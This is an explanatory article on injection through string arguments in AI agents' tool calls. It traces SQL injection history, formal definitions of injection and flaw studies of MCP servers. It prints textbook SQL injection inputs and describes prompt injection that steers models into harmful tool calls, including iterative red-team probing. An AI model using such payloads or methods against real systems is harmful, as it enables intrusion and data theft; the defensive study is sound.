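# String arguments in tool calls that are later read as SQL, shell commands, paths, URLs or regular expressions

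## What does a tool call hand on when an argument is only a string?

A language model produces only text, so it relies on other software to look up an invoice, read a file or send an e-mail. It usually does this through a tool call, a structured request that gives the name of a tool and its arguments, which a program outside the model then carries out. The developer describes each tool beforehand in a tool schema, a machine-readable declaration of the arguments and their types. Tool schemas are usually written in JSON Schema, a standard notation for the structure of data. A schema may require an argument to be a whole number, true or false, or one item from a short list, but very often the type is just "string", which allows any text.

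Another program later parses the string argument according to a grammar and acts on the result. A database parses SQL, the language of database queries; a shell parses commands; a file system parses paths; a network client parses URLs; and a pattern engine parses regular expressions, a compact notation for searching text. These programs are commonly called interpreters. A tool call can match its schema exactly and still make an interpreter do something that neither the developer nor the user intended.

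Many tool calls now follow the Model Context Protocol (MCP), an open standard that Anthropic introduced in 2024 for connecting models to outside tools. An MCP server is a program that offers tools. A client, usually the application around the model, gets the list of tools from the server, shows it to the model and forwards the model's calls. The first revision, Model Context Protocol (2024), gave each tool a name, a description and an `inputSchema`, and the July 2026 revision keeps all three (Model Context Protocol, *Tools*, 2026). *Understanding the Hierarchical Structure and Functional Landscape of the Model Context Protocol* (2026) extracted 1,328,233 tool specifications from source code across 17 marketplaces.

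### One call, from the model to the database

Take an assistant that handles invoices for a small firm. One of its tools, `find_invoices`, needs a customer's name and the column to sort by. The developer's schema reads:

```json
{
  "name": "find_invoices",
  "description": "List a customer's invoices",
  "inputSchema": {
    "type": "object",
    "properties": {
      "customer": { "type": "string" },
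      "sort_by":  { "type": "string" }
    },
    "required": ["customer", "sort_by"]
  }
}
```

A user asks for Acme's invoices, oldest first, and the model writes a JSON call with `"customer": "Acme"` and `"sort_by": "due_date"`. OpenAI's *Function calling* explains that the model only returns the call; the developer's code has to parse the arguments, run the function and send the result back.

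The validator then checks the arguments against the schema. Under JSON Schema (2020), a value passes the `type` keyword if it has one of the listed types, and "string" is one possible type. A fuller validator, like the one in *Gecko* (2026), a simulation environment for tool calls, also checks for missing and undeclared fields, and enforces any numeric bounds, permitted values (`enum`), string lengths and patterns that the schema states. The schema states none of these for `customer` and `sort_by`, so Acme passes, as would any other string. The check uses only the message. *JSON Schema* (2026), a draft from the Internet Engineering Task Force (IETF), counts it as an advantage that validation needs no input or output, but this also means that the validator has no information about the database behind the tool.

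The handler, the function on the server that does the tool's work, then receives two bare strings. The JSON parser has already taken off JSON's own quotation marks. A careless handler pastes the strings into a line of SQL:

```sql
SELECT * FROM invoices WHERE customer = 'Acme' ORDER BY due_date
```

The database receives a single string, with no record of which characters came from the developer and which from the model. It parses the string by its own grammar, in which an apostrophe opens a piece of text, the next apostrophe closes it, and everything outside is part of the instruction.

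Now let the user ask about a customer by the name of O'Brien. JSON gives an apostrophe no special meaning, the schema check passes as before, and the handler builds this:

```sql
SELECT * FROM invoices WHERE customer = 'O'Brien' ORDER BY due_date
```

The database reads the apostrophe in `O'Brien` as the end of the customer's name. It then parses `Brien` as SQL, and the last apostrophe opens a string that never closes. The database returns a syntax error instead of Ms O'Brien's invoices. This is a mild, accidental form of injection, in which an interpreter reads text supplied as data as if it were code. A parameterized query would have avoided the error because it sends the values to the database separately from the query text.

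The invoicing assistant has seven tools in all, and an interpreter sits behind every one.

| Tool | What it is for | Interpreter |
|---|---|---|
| `find_invoices(customer, sort_by)` | list a customer's invoices in a chosen order | database |
| `convert_report(filename)` | turn a report into another format with a command-line program | shell |
| `read_file(path)` | return the contents of a file | path resolver |
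| `fetch_page(url)` | download a web page | URL client |
| `search_notes(pattern)` | find notes that match a pattern | regular-expression engine |
| `run_query(sql)` | run an SQL query | database |
| `run_command(command)` | run a shell command | shell |

The effect of an apostrophe in a string argument depends on what reads the string. If the handler for `convert_report` builds a command line, the filename `O'Brien.pdf` can break it, because the shell, like SQL, treats an apostrophe as an opening quotation mark. In a path or a regular expression, the apostrophe is an ordinary character. But in a regular expression the dot means "any character", so a search for `O'Brien.pdf` also finds `O'Brien-pdf`. Whether a string is harmless therefore depends on which interpreter reads it and where the string appears in that interpreter's input, and a schema that says "string" records neither.

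Declaring an argument a "string" rules out very little. Suppose `find_invoices` had a third argument, the invoice's status, with the permitted values draft, sent and paid. A developer could test all three. A string of exactly 64 printable ASCII characters (95 including the space) can take 95<sup>64</sup> forms, or about 10<sup>126</sup>, and a bare "string" has no length limit. Whole numbers are unlimited too, but the database treats an amount of 7 and an amount of 7,000,000 alike, as numbers. Strings differ in kind, since they include names, misspelt names, fragments of SQL and complete commands, and the schema puts them all in one class.

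### What a checker can know

Nobody can yet establish everything a large model will do by inspecting it. But if a model acts only through tool calls, a checker, software that decides whether a tool call may run, can examine each call beforehand. The checker has to examine only a small, well-formed message instead of billions of parameters. From `"status": "paid"` it can work out everything the argument is able to do. From `"customer"` followed by free text, it can conclude only that some text will reach a handler. What the text does after that depends on the handler's code and the interpreter's grammar, and neither is in the message.

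*Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents* (2026) counts tool schemas as part of the trusted computing base, the components whose correctness everything else depends on, and warns that a call "may pass type checks while violating task purpose". Its example is an e-mail tool whose message body is a valid string but contains customer data from a different task. No interpreter misreads the string, but a type check cannot detect that it is the wrong one to send.

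A human reviewer is only a little better off. The Model Context Protocol recommends that a person always be able to deny a tool call, and that clients show the user the inputs before calling the server. The approval screen would show the name O'Brien, but not the SQL that the handler will build from it.

Strict schema enforcement prevents malformed tool calls but barely restricts what goes inside a free-form string. Anthropic's *Strict tool use* describes grammar-constrained sampling, in which the software that picks the model's next piece of text allows only continuations that fit the schema. If a booking tool expects a whole number of passengers, the call contains 2 and never "two". OpenAI has a strict mode for the same purpose. According to Anthropic's page, developers need not validate and retry tool calls, which is fair for `passengers`. However, the page's first sample tool has a `unit`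 argument that must be celsius or fahrenheit and a `location` argument that may be any string, and within `location` the sampler is almost as free as before.

Outside strict mode, even a declared limit may not be enforced. *MCPGuard* (2026), a study of the software kits developers use to build MCP programs, uses the term "structural gap" for an implementation that accepts a message the schema rejects. It covers the protocol's own messages, not the arguments of individual tools, but for those arguments too, a checker can safely rely on a constraint only if something is known to enforce it.

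The name O'Brien came from an honest user, but text in a tool call may also come from people the user has never met. A model that reads a supplier's e-mail, a web page or an old note may follow an instruction in it as if the user had written it. This is called prompt injection. *Explanation-Bound Tool Execution for AI Agents* (2026) cites earlier studies in which untrusted content redirected tool-using agents in this way.

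Sun, Kang and colleagues (2026), in *VIPER-MCP*, describe an attacker who controls only some text that the agent has to process, and who never calls the server's functions or tampers with the protocol's messages. The agent selects a tool and fills in arguments of the right type, which pass the type check and carry the attacker's text to functions that start programs, send network requests or open files. According to the paper, MCP standardizes the format of a call but enforces no conditions on what the call means.

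The damage such a call can do has probably grown. *An Empirical Study of Model Context Protocol Applications* (2026) reports an analysis by Stein of 177,436 tools in public repositories. Tools that directly change something in the outside world rose from 27% to 65% of tool usage between November 2024 and February 2026.

### Values and programs

The seven tools take two kinds of string that the schema cannot distinguish. A customer's name is a value argument, meant as plain data, and no part of it should ever act as code. The `sql` of `run_query` and the `command` of `run_command` are program arguments, which are meant to be run. The database is supposed to execute the text that `run_query` receives, but if it executes part of a customer's name, the handler has a bug. Sun and colleagues make the same distinction, and their count of vulnerabilities leaves out any tool whose purpose is to run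 arbitrary commands.

Many real tools take a program as an argument. The MCP documentation has a sample tool, `execute_sql`, whose `query` argument has the type "string" and the description "The SQL query to execute". The software developer Simon Willison wrote a plugin that gives models access to databases through his program Datasette, and one of its three tools takes a database name and a string of SQL. Anthropic's *Tool use with Claude* lists a ready-made tool that runs bash, a widely used shell, in the developer's own application. OpenAI offers custom tools that take free-form text, with no JSON Schema for the input.

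None of the characters in a value argument should act as code, so the developer can aim for a complete fix, either by keeping the interpreter from parsing the value or by narrowing the strings the tool accepts. Neither works for `run_query`, because the database has to parse the query. There the developer can try to judge the program before it runs, or limit what any program can reach. Willison did the latter by making his SQL tool read-only for the time being. That limit isn't visible in the argument, which is a string of SQL whether or not the tool can write to the database.

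Paths, URLs and search patterns fit this division less neatly. The path passed to `read_file` is a value argument, because the user means it to name one file, but the path resolver has to parse all of it. The `sort_by` argument of `find_invoices` is awkward in another way, because it names a database column and so goes where SQL expects part of the query's structure.

### How loosely developers type their tools

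An audit of web services in general gives some idea of how common loose declarations are. *SilentProbe* (Li, Guo and colleagues, 2026) examined 721,320 parameters in 2,501 public descriptions of web services written in OpenAPI, a machine-readable format for what a service accepts. It counts a parameter as machine-checkable if its schema declares an enumeration of permitted values, a pattern, a named format such as a date, or numeric bounds. Enumerations appeared in 7.5% of the parameters, patterns or formats in 6.6%, and numeric bounds in 1.1%, for a total of 15.2%. For the remaining 84.8%, a validator can check at most the type.

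Those figures cover API parameters of every type, not only strings, and services that developers wrote for all kinds of callers, not only AI agents. The 84.8% counted as unconstrained includes true-or-false parameters, although their type already limits them to two values, so it is not the share of bare strings. The count of checkable parameters includes those with a `format`, but in the IETF draft on validation that keyword is mainly an annotation, which validators need not enforce.

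Li and colleagues tested the effect of missing constraints by calling live services. One people-search service, whose schema declared seniority only as a string, returned 28,417 results for `vp` and none for `vice_president`, without an error in either case. Across 27 vendors, they sent altered values and set aside those that the server interpreted correctly. Where the schema contained a machine-checkable constraint, all 111 remaining values produced an error. Where only the prose description stated the constraint, 44 of 61 failed silently. A single schema validator checked requests to all the vendors and raised 110 of the 111 errors before the request reached a vendor. The validator belongs to Monid, a company with which Li and colleagues disclose an affiliation, but the count of 721,320 parameters does not depend on the validator.

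They also gave twelve language models a parameter for a person's department, whose description gave one of the eighteen accepted terms as an example. All 88 attempts gave a value outside the accepted vocabulary. When the schema listed all eighteen terms as an enumeration, none of 89 attempts did. These were honest mistakes on ordinary tasks and are little evidence about attackers, but in both cases the validator can refuse only what the schema rules out.

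Afsar (2026), in *What a Random Draw from the MCP Registry Contains*, avoided the usual bias towards popular servers by sampling at random from servers that offer tools to AI agents. He drew 400 of the 7,258 servers in the official registry that run locally as packages from npm, a public software library, and tried to start each one once. Only 195 completed the protocol's opening exchange. These advertised 2,766 tools, none of which had a fatal schema error, meaning a missing schema, an invalid type, or a malformed list of properties or required fields. The schemas of both `find_invoices` and `run_command` would pass this test, since a valid schema need not be restrictive, and Afsar did not measure how restrictive the sampled schemas were. He did find that 58.8% of the tools carried none of the optional annotations that indicate, for example, whether a tool only reads data or can also destroy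 it.

Developers often write restrictions in prose, which a model can read and follow but a schema validator cannot enforce. *Mitigating Taint-Style Vulnerabilities in MCP Servers via Security-Aware Tool Descriptions* (2026) examined 1,856 MCP tools and found operational constraints, such as input requirements, in 77.21% of the parameter descriptions and security guidance in 1.83%. In 40.1% of their public documents, Li and colleagues found at least one constraint that appeared in prose but not in the schema.

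## What is an injection, and how was it first understood?

Web programmers had the O'Brien problem long before language models called tools. In the 1990s many websites ran small programs called CGI scripts, which took the text a visitor typed into a form and sent back a page. A script often pasted that text into a command line and passed the result to the shell. Some characters, called metacharacters, have a special meaning to the shell. A semicolon, for example, ends one command and lets another begin, so if a visitor's semicolon reached the shell, whatever followed it ran as a command on the web server. *Safe CGI Programming* (1995), an early guide, summarized the lesson as "Never trust input data".

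### Lists of dangerous characters

The usual defence was a blocklist, a list of characters to remove or make harmless. A script called phf, which passed visitors' queries to a directory program, used a routine that put a backslash before each of twenty characters so that the shell would treat them as ordinary text. The list left out the newline, which ends a command just as a semicolon does. Attackers exploited the script widely in 1996 and 1997, according to *phf CGI Script fails to guard against newline characters* (2001), a note from the CERT Coordination Center, a US centre that tracks software flaws.

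Jennifer Myers had pointed out the missing newline on Bugtraq, a security mailing list, on 5 February 1996. She was discussing published guidelines that, like the phf routine, listed twenty characters, and she said she had never seen the newline in any such list. The two lists shared sixteen characters. The other four were the question mark, tilde, caret and backslash in the phf routine, and the exclamation mark, hash, colon and slash in the guidelines.

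Myers suggested adding the newline. Andersen (1996) answered the same day that this would close the hole but repeat the mistake behind it. The next morning Cohen (1996) proposed the opposite policy, an allowlist, which keeps only the symbols known to be safe and drops everything else. In November 1997 the CERT Coordination Center's *Sanitizing User-Supplied Data in CGI Scripts* (1997) gave the same advice, because the author of a blocklist has to predict every possible input.

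Allowlists can be wrong too. The sample code in the first version of that advisory accidentally let through the backslash and both square brackets. Bacon (1997) pointed this out a day later, and CERT corrected it the day after that. The corrected sample keeps letters, digits, the hyphen, underscore, full stop and @ sign, and replaces any other character with an underscore. This turns O'Brien into O_Brien, so a search using the altered name will not find a record stored under O'Brien.

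### Escaping, and the numbers without quotation marks

Databases had the same fault. *NT Web Technology Vulnerabilities* (rain.forest.puppy, 1998), an article in the hacker magazine *Phrack*, showed that a visitor to a web page could add SQL statements to the one its developer had written. Microsoft's database server accepted several statements in one message. rain.forest.puppy wrote that Microsoft, when told of the flaw, said it was not a problem. Security writers commonly treat the article as the first public account of SQL injection, though it does not use that name.

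One type of page on Microsoft's web server already defended against this by doubling every apostrophe in the visitor's text. Inside a quoted string, SQL treats two apostrophes in a row as one literal apostrophe, so `'O''Brien'` is a correct way to write her name. Rewriting a special character so that the interpreter treats it as plain text is called escaping. Unlike deleting characters, escaping keeps the data intact. But SQL puts no quotation marks around numbers, so in a query that looks up a phone number, the visitor can add SQL after the digits without using an apostrophe.

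rain.forest.puppy advised developers to double the apostrophes in text and to check that a number consists only of digits. Better still, the article went on, they should stop pasting text into SQL and pass the visitor's values as parameters to procedures stored in the database, an idea that parameterized queries share.

Filtering and escaping nevertheless remained common for years. In 2006, *The Essence of Command Injection Attacks in Web Applications*, by Su and Wassermann, listed defenses that included blocklists of known attack strings, length limits, pattern filters, PHP's automatic insertion of backslashes, and several commercial products. In the paper's example, a shop's web page escapes apostrophes by doubling them in both the customer's name and the credit card type. The card type is a number, so the input `2 OR 1=1` needs no apostrophes, and the page returns every card number in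 the table.

Escaping a value protects only the query it was escaped for. The database correctly stores the escaped name as plain O'Brien, so if another part of the program later fetches the name and pastes it into a new query without escaping it again, the apostrophe ends the string. Su and Wassermann mention attacks built on this, known as second-order attacks, among the ways round escaping. All these defences work on the characters of the input without checking where they end up in the finished query. The word OR, for example, changes the query only when it stands outside the quotation marks, so it has no effect inside a firm name such as "Now OR Never".

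### Injection as a matter of parse trees

Su and Wassermann therefore defined injection in terms of the finished query, in what they described as the first formal definition. Before a database runs a query, it works out the query's structure using a grammar, a set of rules such as "a condition may be a comparison" or "a condition may be two conditions joined by OR". The result is a parse tree, with the whole query at the top, its clauses branching off below, and its words and symbols as the leaves.

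With the customer Acme, the condition in the query of `find_invoices` has this tree:

```
condition
└─ comparison
   ├─ column: customer
   ├─ =
   └─ string
      ├─ '
      ├─ text: Acme
      └─ '
```

The input, `Acme`, fills one node, the text between the quotation marks. Now let the customer's name be the textbook input `' OR '1'='1`. The handler builds `customer = '' OR '1'='1'`, and the tree becomes:

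```
condition
├─ comparison
│  ├─ column: customer
│  ├─ =
│  └─ string: ''
├─ OR
└─ comparison
   ├─ string: '1'
   ├─ =
   └─ string: '1'
```

Since '1' always equals '1', the database returns every customer's invoices. The input runs from the second apostrophe of the empty string, through the OR, to the last 1, just before the closing apostrophe. The only node that covers all of it is the condition at the top, which also covers `customer =` and two apostrophes that the developer wrote, so no node has exactly the input beneath it.

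The definition tests for this difference using a set *U* of grammar symbols that the developer allows inputs to take, such as text, numbers and column names. An input has a valid syntactic form if some node in the parse tree has a symbol from *U* and its leaves are exactly the input. A query is an injection attack if it parses and at least one of its inputs lacks a valid syntactic form. The unescaped O'Brien query is an error rather than an attack under this definition, because it doesn't parse and the database never runs it.

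What counts as an attack depends on *U*. Bugzilla, a program for tracking software bugs, lets users save search conditions and run them again later. A whole condition is a proper input there, even one that is always true and so filters nothing out. A developer of such a program would include conditions in *U*. For the `customer` argument, *U* should contain only text.

### Checking the finished query

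Su and Wassermann's program, SQLCheck, uses markers to record which characters of a finished query came from the input. It puts an opening and a closing marker, written here as ⟪ and ⟫, around every input before the application uses it, and the markers travel with the input into the query. SQLCheck then parses the marked query with an altered grammar. For each symbol *v* in *U* the alteration adds a new symbol *v*ᵃ with two rules:

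```
vᵃ → v
vᵃ → ⟪ v ⟫
```

It also replaces *v* with *v*ᵃ wherever *v* appears on the right-hand side of another rule. Markers can therefore surround only one complete piece of a permitted kind. The condition `customer = '⟪Acme⟫'` parses because the markers enclose a complete text. The condition `customer = '⟪' OR '1'='1⟫'` doesn't, because no rule allows a marker to open in one string and close in another. If the marked query parses, SQLCheck removes the markers and sends the query to the database. Otherwise, it blocks the query.

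Su and Wassermann proved that this procedure lets a query through if and only if the query belongs to the grammar and is not an injection attack. It therefore misses no attack (soundness) and blocks no legitimate query (completeness). Both results depend on the definition of an injection attack and on several conditions. The grammar has to match the SQL that the database accepts, and *U* has to express what the developer wants to allow. The developer's own part of the query has to be right, because the definition treats it as the statement of intent. The proof also assumes that the application marks every input and checks every query.

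In tests on five web applications, each in a PHP and a Java version, SQLCheck blocked all 18,424 attacks and allowed all 3,824 legitimate requests per language, taking about three milliseconds a query. The attack strings came from published exploits that another research group had collected, and none were written to defeat SQLCheck, so the perfect score mainly shows that the program does what the theorem predicts. Su and Wassermann describe a weakness that the tests could not reveal. Their markers were random four-letter strings, so an attacker who tried enough combinations could find them and forge a marker. Su and Wassermann propose escaping any marker that occurs in the input.

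### A rival definition

Most later work kept the idea that an attack alters the structure of the query. Ray and Ligatti rejected it in *Defining Code-injection Attacks* (2012). In their counterexample, an application pastes an unquoted value into a query that checks a PIN. The input is the function call `exit()`, so the condition becomes `pin=exit()`. The input fills exactly one node of the parse tree and so counts as intended structure, yet it makes the database run a function that the developer never asked for.

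Su and Wassermann's definition can handle this by leaving function calls out of *U*. Ray and Ligatti reply that an engineer has no clear way to know which symbols to leave out, and may want to allow a form in one place and refuse it in another, which they say is impossible in SQLCheck. Su and Wassermann's paper does describe a separate policy for each pairing of an input with a query, so the second objection applies mainly to using a single policy for a whole application. The first objection still holds, because although the theorem is exact, the developer must first choose *U*, which is the hardest decision.

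The structural test also raises false alarms. Ray and Ligatti describe an application that joins two inputs, a file name and an extension, into one quoted string such as `'f.e'`. Neither input is a complete string, so SQLCheck would block a harmless query. The invoicing assistant would have the same problem if its handler wrote `'INV-` and let the model supply only the digits of an invoice number.

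Their own definition starts from what is *not* code. A closed value is a finished piece of data that has nothing left to compute and no names left to look up, such as the number 7, the string 'Acme' or the constant TRUE. Every symbol of a query that lies outside all closed values is code. In their notation, symbol *i* of a program *p* is code if no stretch of *p* that contains *i* forms a closed value, and an injection occurs exactly when

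∃*i* : tainted(*p*ᵢ) ∧ Code(*p*, *i*)

that is, when at least one symbol copied from an untrusted input serves as code. In the textbook input `' OR '1'='1` the apostrophes and the 1s belong to string values and are harmless. The OR, the equals sign and the spaces are code.

Applied to the invoicing assistant, with a policy for Su and Wassermann that permits text, numbers and column names, the definitions give these verdicts:

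| Input, as the handler uses it | Su and Wassermann | Ray and Ligatti |
|---|---|---|
| `Acme` as a quoted customer name | allowed | allowed |
| `' OR '1'='1` as a quoted customer name | attack | injection |
| `0042` after a fixed `INV-` in a quoted string | attack | allowed |
| `due_date` as the column to sort by | allowed | injection |
| a whole query, for `run_query` | attack, unless *U* includes whole queries | injection |

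Ray and Ligatti's definition works better for value arguments. It classifies the first three rows correctly and doesn't require anyone to write a policy. A customer's name should only ever be a closed value, and the developer can state that rule without knowing SQL's grammar. Their definition is too strict for `sort_by`, because the database has to look up a column name, so every ordinary call counts as an injection. Su and Wassermann's permitted forms suit `sort_by` better, although a policy that allows column names allows all of them, including columns the user should not be able to sort by.

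Neither definition helps much with `run_query`, whose argument is a program by design. Ray and Ligatti accept this, mentioning tools that let administrators type in SQL as a case where injection is expected, and they do not make their definition depend on whether anyone meant harm. Both definitions also allow a well-formed but wrong value, such as another customer's name that a prompt injection led the model to fill in.

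Ray and Ligatti also proved that, in a small model of SQL, every program that always copies some untrusted input into its query without examining it is open to injection. The proof shows how to construct an attack for each kind of value the input might appear in, whether a string, a number or a constant such as TRUE. A developer can therefore tell that a handler like the first version of `find_invoices` is unsafe without testing an attack. The theorem does not cover handlers that inspect or escape the input first.

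Both definitions require a record of which characters came from outside. Ray and Ligatti would obtain it by taint tracking. They object to SQLCheck's markers because the application can read them and may behave differently as a result. In a tool handler, this record is at least easy to start, because each argument arrives separately and comes entirely from the model.

In *Abstract Code Injection*, Buro and Mastroeni later observed that many approaches try to prevent code injection but few address the harder problem of defining it.

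### Input as a language

Language-theoretic security, or LangSec, applies the same kind of reasoning to all input. Len Sassaman, Meredith Patterson, Sergey Bratus and others developed it from about 2011. Patterson had already built a defence against SQL injection on this basis as a doctoral student in 2005, and it was the first of its kind according to a biographical note in *The Bugs We Have to Kill* (Bratus, Patterson and Shubina, 2015). In formal language theory, a language is a set of strings, and a recognizer is a program that decides whether a string belongs to that set. Under LangSec, developers define the language of acceptable inputs and use a recognizer to accept or reject each input as a whole before any other code acts on it.

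In *Shotgun parsers in the cross-hairs*, Bratus and Patterson (2012) use the term "shotgun parser" for the habit of scattering input checks through the code that does the work. Suppose the handler for `convert_report` creates an output file, then reads the rest of the filename and finds an unacceptable extension. It rejects the input only after acting on part of it. A keynote at the security conference Troopers (2015) recommended that programs finish checking the syntax before they act, even if this means scanning a message to its end.

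Some input formats allow no complete recognizer. In *The Science of Insecurity*, Sassaman, Patterson and Bratus (2011) attribute a huge share of insecurity to protocols and message formats whose safe processing would require solving provably unsolvable problems. The best known of these is the halting problem, which is to decide, for every program, whether it will ever finish. A format that can contain arbitrary programs raises such problems. According to the abstract of a related talk at 28C3, a hacker congress, nobody can comprehensively test implementations of such formats either.

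For tool arguments, this means that recognition is more useful for a name than for a command. A developer can define the language of customer names in one line, say up to eighty letters, spaces, full stops, hyphens and apostrophes, and easily write a recognizer for it. But O'Brien belongs to that language, and a handler that pastes her name into SQL unescaped will still break the query. Recognition keeps out inputs the tool never needed, but the handler still has to pass the accepted ones on safely. For `run_command`, the language is the shell's own, and a developer who knows that a command is well formed still knows very little about what it will do.

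### When two programs parse the same input differently

LangSec's other main lesson is that when one program checks a message and another acts on it, the check protects the system only if both parse the message in the same way. *Security Applications of Formal Language Theory* (Sassaman, Patterson and colleagues, 2011) formalized the attack that exploits a difference in parsing and called it a parse tree differential attack. The Troopers keynote traces the problem back to 1998 work on systems that monitor network traffic for intruders, which may piece together the same traffic differently from the computers they guard. It also cites a 2010 study of the certificates that verify a website's identity.

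HTTP request smuggling is the classic case. Many websites have a front server that receives visitors' requests, applies access rules, and passes the requests to a back server over a shared connection. The requests arrive there as one stream of text, so both servers have to work out where each request ends. In HTTP/1.1, the sender can either give the length of the body in advance or send the body in chunks and mark the end with an empty chunk. If a request uses both methods and they conflict, the front server may go by one and the back server by the other. The back server then reads what the front server took to be the end of one request as the beginning of the next. It may carry out a request that the front server never checked, or attach the leftover text to another visitor's request.

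Neither server needs to have a bug that would show up when tested alone. The HTTP standard has a rule for conflicting lengths, but it helps only if both servers follow it, and many programs try to make sense of irregular input instead of rejecting it. Two programs that do this are likely to interpret some irregular messages differently. LangSec therefore favours strict recognizers and formats simple enough for independent programmers to implement the same way.

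Even in a small system, a tool call passes through several parsers. The validator and the handler may use different JSON libraries, and if a call contains the key `customer` twice, one library may keep the first value and the other the last. The validator can then approve one name while the handler uses another. Similarly, some databases treat a backslash before an apostrophe as an escape, and others treat it as an ordinary character. A SQL checker that follows the wrong convention can misidentify where a string ends and approve a query that the database parses differently.

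SQLCheck's guarantee holds only for the grammar that SQLCheck uses, which may differ from the database's. Su and Wassermann considered building the check into the database's own parser, which would remove the mismatch. They decided against it because developers often move web applications between databases, and the protection could disappear without them noticing. For a tool server that stays with one database, the database's own parser looks like the safer choice.

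## How often do AI agents' tools turn arguments into code by mistake?

On a 1990s website, visitors typed the values that went into the programmer's query. In a tool call, a language model writes the values. If a user asks the invoicing assistant to convert a report that a supplier emailed, the model may take the filename it passes to `convert_report` from the user's request or the supplier's message, or it may guess. The handler receives only a string, so it can't tell where the filename came from.

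Text from an outsider can also affect an argument some time after the agent receives it. Wu, Yao and colleagues (2026) point out in *ChainFuzzer* that an agent may store what one tool returns and later pass it to another. For example, text that `fetch_page` downloads on Monday could end up in a filename on Friday.

An outsider can sometimes dictate a whole tool call. *ToFu* (2026), which describes a testing program for agents' tools, asked models to repeat a text that contained a tool's name and arguments. In six agent frameworks, the software around the model treated the repeated text as a genuine tool call, according to Divya's *Researchers Discover 253 Security Vulnerabilities Across 343 AI Agent Tools* (2026).

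More often, the model changes the text before passing it to a tool. Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian (2026), in *From Prompt Injection to Web Exploitation*, note that a model may generate, decode or rewrite harmful content, so the interpreter may receive text that wasn't in anything the model read. In their analysis, the flaw is usually in a database or command runner that trusts its input too much, and the model gives an outsider a way to influence that input.

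### The model has no boundary, but the interpreter does

*Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, written by David C and published by the UK's National Cyber Security Centre in December 2025, warns security professionals against treating prompt injection as a new form of SQL injection. A database engine carries out instructions, and stores data or uses it in a query, so a parameterized query can keep the two apart whatever the input contains. A language model receives the developer's instructions, the user's request and a supplier's e-mail as one run of text, and predicts the next token, a word or piece of a word. Developers can train the model to give priority to some passages, or mark others as data, but it has no built-in distinction between instructions and data. David C concludes that prompt injection may never have a complete remedy like the one for SQL injection.

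He prefers to compare the model to a confused deputy, a program with privileges that someone without them tricks into acting for them. Programmers can fix an ordinary confused deputy, but he calls a model "inherently confusable". Developers should therefore assume that some attacks will succeed and limit the damage with deterministic code that restricts what the system can do. He also likes a rule of thumb from a public discussion between Simon Willison and Baibhav Bista, that a model processing someone's text should have only that person's privileges. Under this rule, the invoicing assistant could not use `run_command` while reading a supplier's e-mail.

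David C's argument is about the model, not the interpreter behind the tool. Suppose a prompt injection succeeds and the supplier dictates the `customer` argument. If the handler sends the value as a parameter, the database looks for a customer with that exact text as a name and finds none. The supplier can still get the model to request a real customer's invoices, which is the residual risk he describes, but cannot turn the name into SQL. Injection into the interpreter can be prevented even though injection into the model cannot, so it matters how many tool developers have taken the steps to prevent it.

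### Counting flaws in code and on live servers

Sun and colleagues carried out the largest search that confirmed flaws by triggering them. Their program, VIPER-MCP, first searches a server's source code for paths by which a tool's argument can reach a function that runs commands, opens URLs or handles files without an adequate check. It then starts the server, connects a model to it and writes ordinary-language requests intended to make the model call the tool with a harmful argument. Monitoring code inside the server records what arrives at the function. Sun and colleagues counted a flaw only if the call had an observable effect.

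Researchers scanned 39,884 public code repositories and confirmed 106 previously unknown flaws, about one for every 376 repositories. At the time of writing, 67 of the flaws had an identifier in CVE, the public catalogue of security flaws.

The true rate must be higher. The search covered only three classes of flaw, and it left out SQL injection and tools meant to run arbitrary commands. It could also test only servers that start in isolation, which ruled out some that depend on outside services.

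In a test on 130 servers with known flaws, VIPER-MCP missed ten, or 7.7%. But Sun and colleagues had used VIPER-MCP to find 67 of those servers. If all ten misses are among the other 63, the miss rate for those is 16%.

The trials also show how much a model can alter an argument. One server had a tool that took a web address as a string, extracted a project number from it and inserted that value into a file path without checking that it was numeric. The model kept supplying addresses with ordinary numeric identifiers, even when the request contained something else, so a single test would not have revealed the flaw. On another server, the model escaped quotation marks in a suspicious argument before sending it. In both cases, VIPER-MCP needed several rounds of feedback before a harmful value arrived intact.

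This habit protects a server only against attackers who give up early. With OpenAI's GPT-5.4 in every role, VIPER-MCP triggered flaws in 120 of the 130 servers. When GPT-5.4-mini wrote and revised the attacks instead, it triggered them in 83 to 88, depending on which of five models operated the tools. Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian found large differences between seven models in their own test application. This may be because they used five fixed scenarios, whereas VIPER-MCP revised each request after a failure. A model's tidying can also cause errors. If it doubles the apostrophe in O'Brien and the handler correctly uses a parameterized query, the database will search for a name with two apostrophes.

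In *Hunt Them All*, Oliveira and Fiser of the security company Trend Micro describe using language models to review about 19,000 repositories. An agent based on Google's Gemini reported 17,558 vulnerabilities, and a second pass with the same model, meant to remove mistakes, left just over 15,000. They gave a random sample of 2,287 of these to an agent based on a Claude model, which kept 438. They then examined the 438 by hand and confirmed 93 as exploitable.

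SQL injection was the most common type among the 93, at 26%. David C writes that it is now rare in websites, so a new group of developers seems to be repeating the old mistake.

From these figures Oliveira and Fiser estimate that between 600 and 1,650 of the repositories contain exploitable flaws. They get their central figure of about 770 by applying a rate of 4.1% (93 of 2,287) to 19,000 repositories. But 4.1% is a share of reported vulnerabilities, and one repository can have several. Applying it to the 15,000 reports from which they drew the sample gives roughly 610 flaws, perhaps in fewer repositories. The number would be higher if the Claude agent wrongly discarded real flaws, but they did not measure whether it did.

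Source code does not show how people deploy a server. In *Exposed by Design*, Padilla (2026) identified 640 servers on the public internet in July 2026 and tested 414 of them by calling their tools directly, without a model. He filed 68 security advisories after checking the findings by hand. His program found signs of command injection, a class in which he includes SQL injection, on 38 servers and signs of server-side request forgery on 29. In server-side request forgery, an outsider gets a server to send requests to an address the outsider chooses. These counts are estimates because the program relied on indirect evidence such as a slow reply. One server can also appear in several classes.

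Padilla worked alone and could not reach servers that run only on a user's own computer, which he thinks may be the majority. The set of servers he measured also changes quickly. Of 464 servers he confirmed on 21 July, 193 were gone three days later.

*ToFu* looks for tools that don't behave as described. Its program reads a tool's description and schema, selects suitable checks from a collection of 74, and calls the tool repeatedly with varied inputs that fit the schema. For example, a tool fails if it is described as reading files only within one folder but reads a file elsewhere. A language model helps choose the checks and initial inputs, but ordinary code decides whether the tool has broken a rule. The paper reports 253 verified bugs, affecting 343 of 3,405 tools and 118 of 273 repositories. Divya cautions that such a bug is a defect in the tool and does not prove that attackers could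 exploit every deployment of it.

| Source | Examined | Counted as a flaw | Result |
|---|---|---|---|
| Sun and colleagues | 39,884 repositories | a new command, URL or path flaw, triggered through a model | 106 flaws, 0.27 per 100 repositories |
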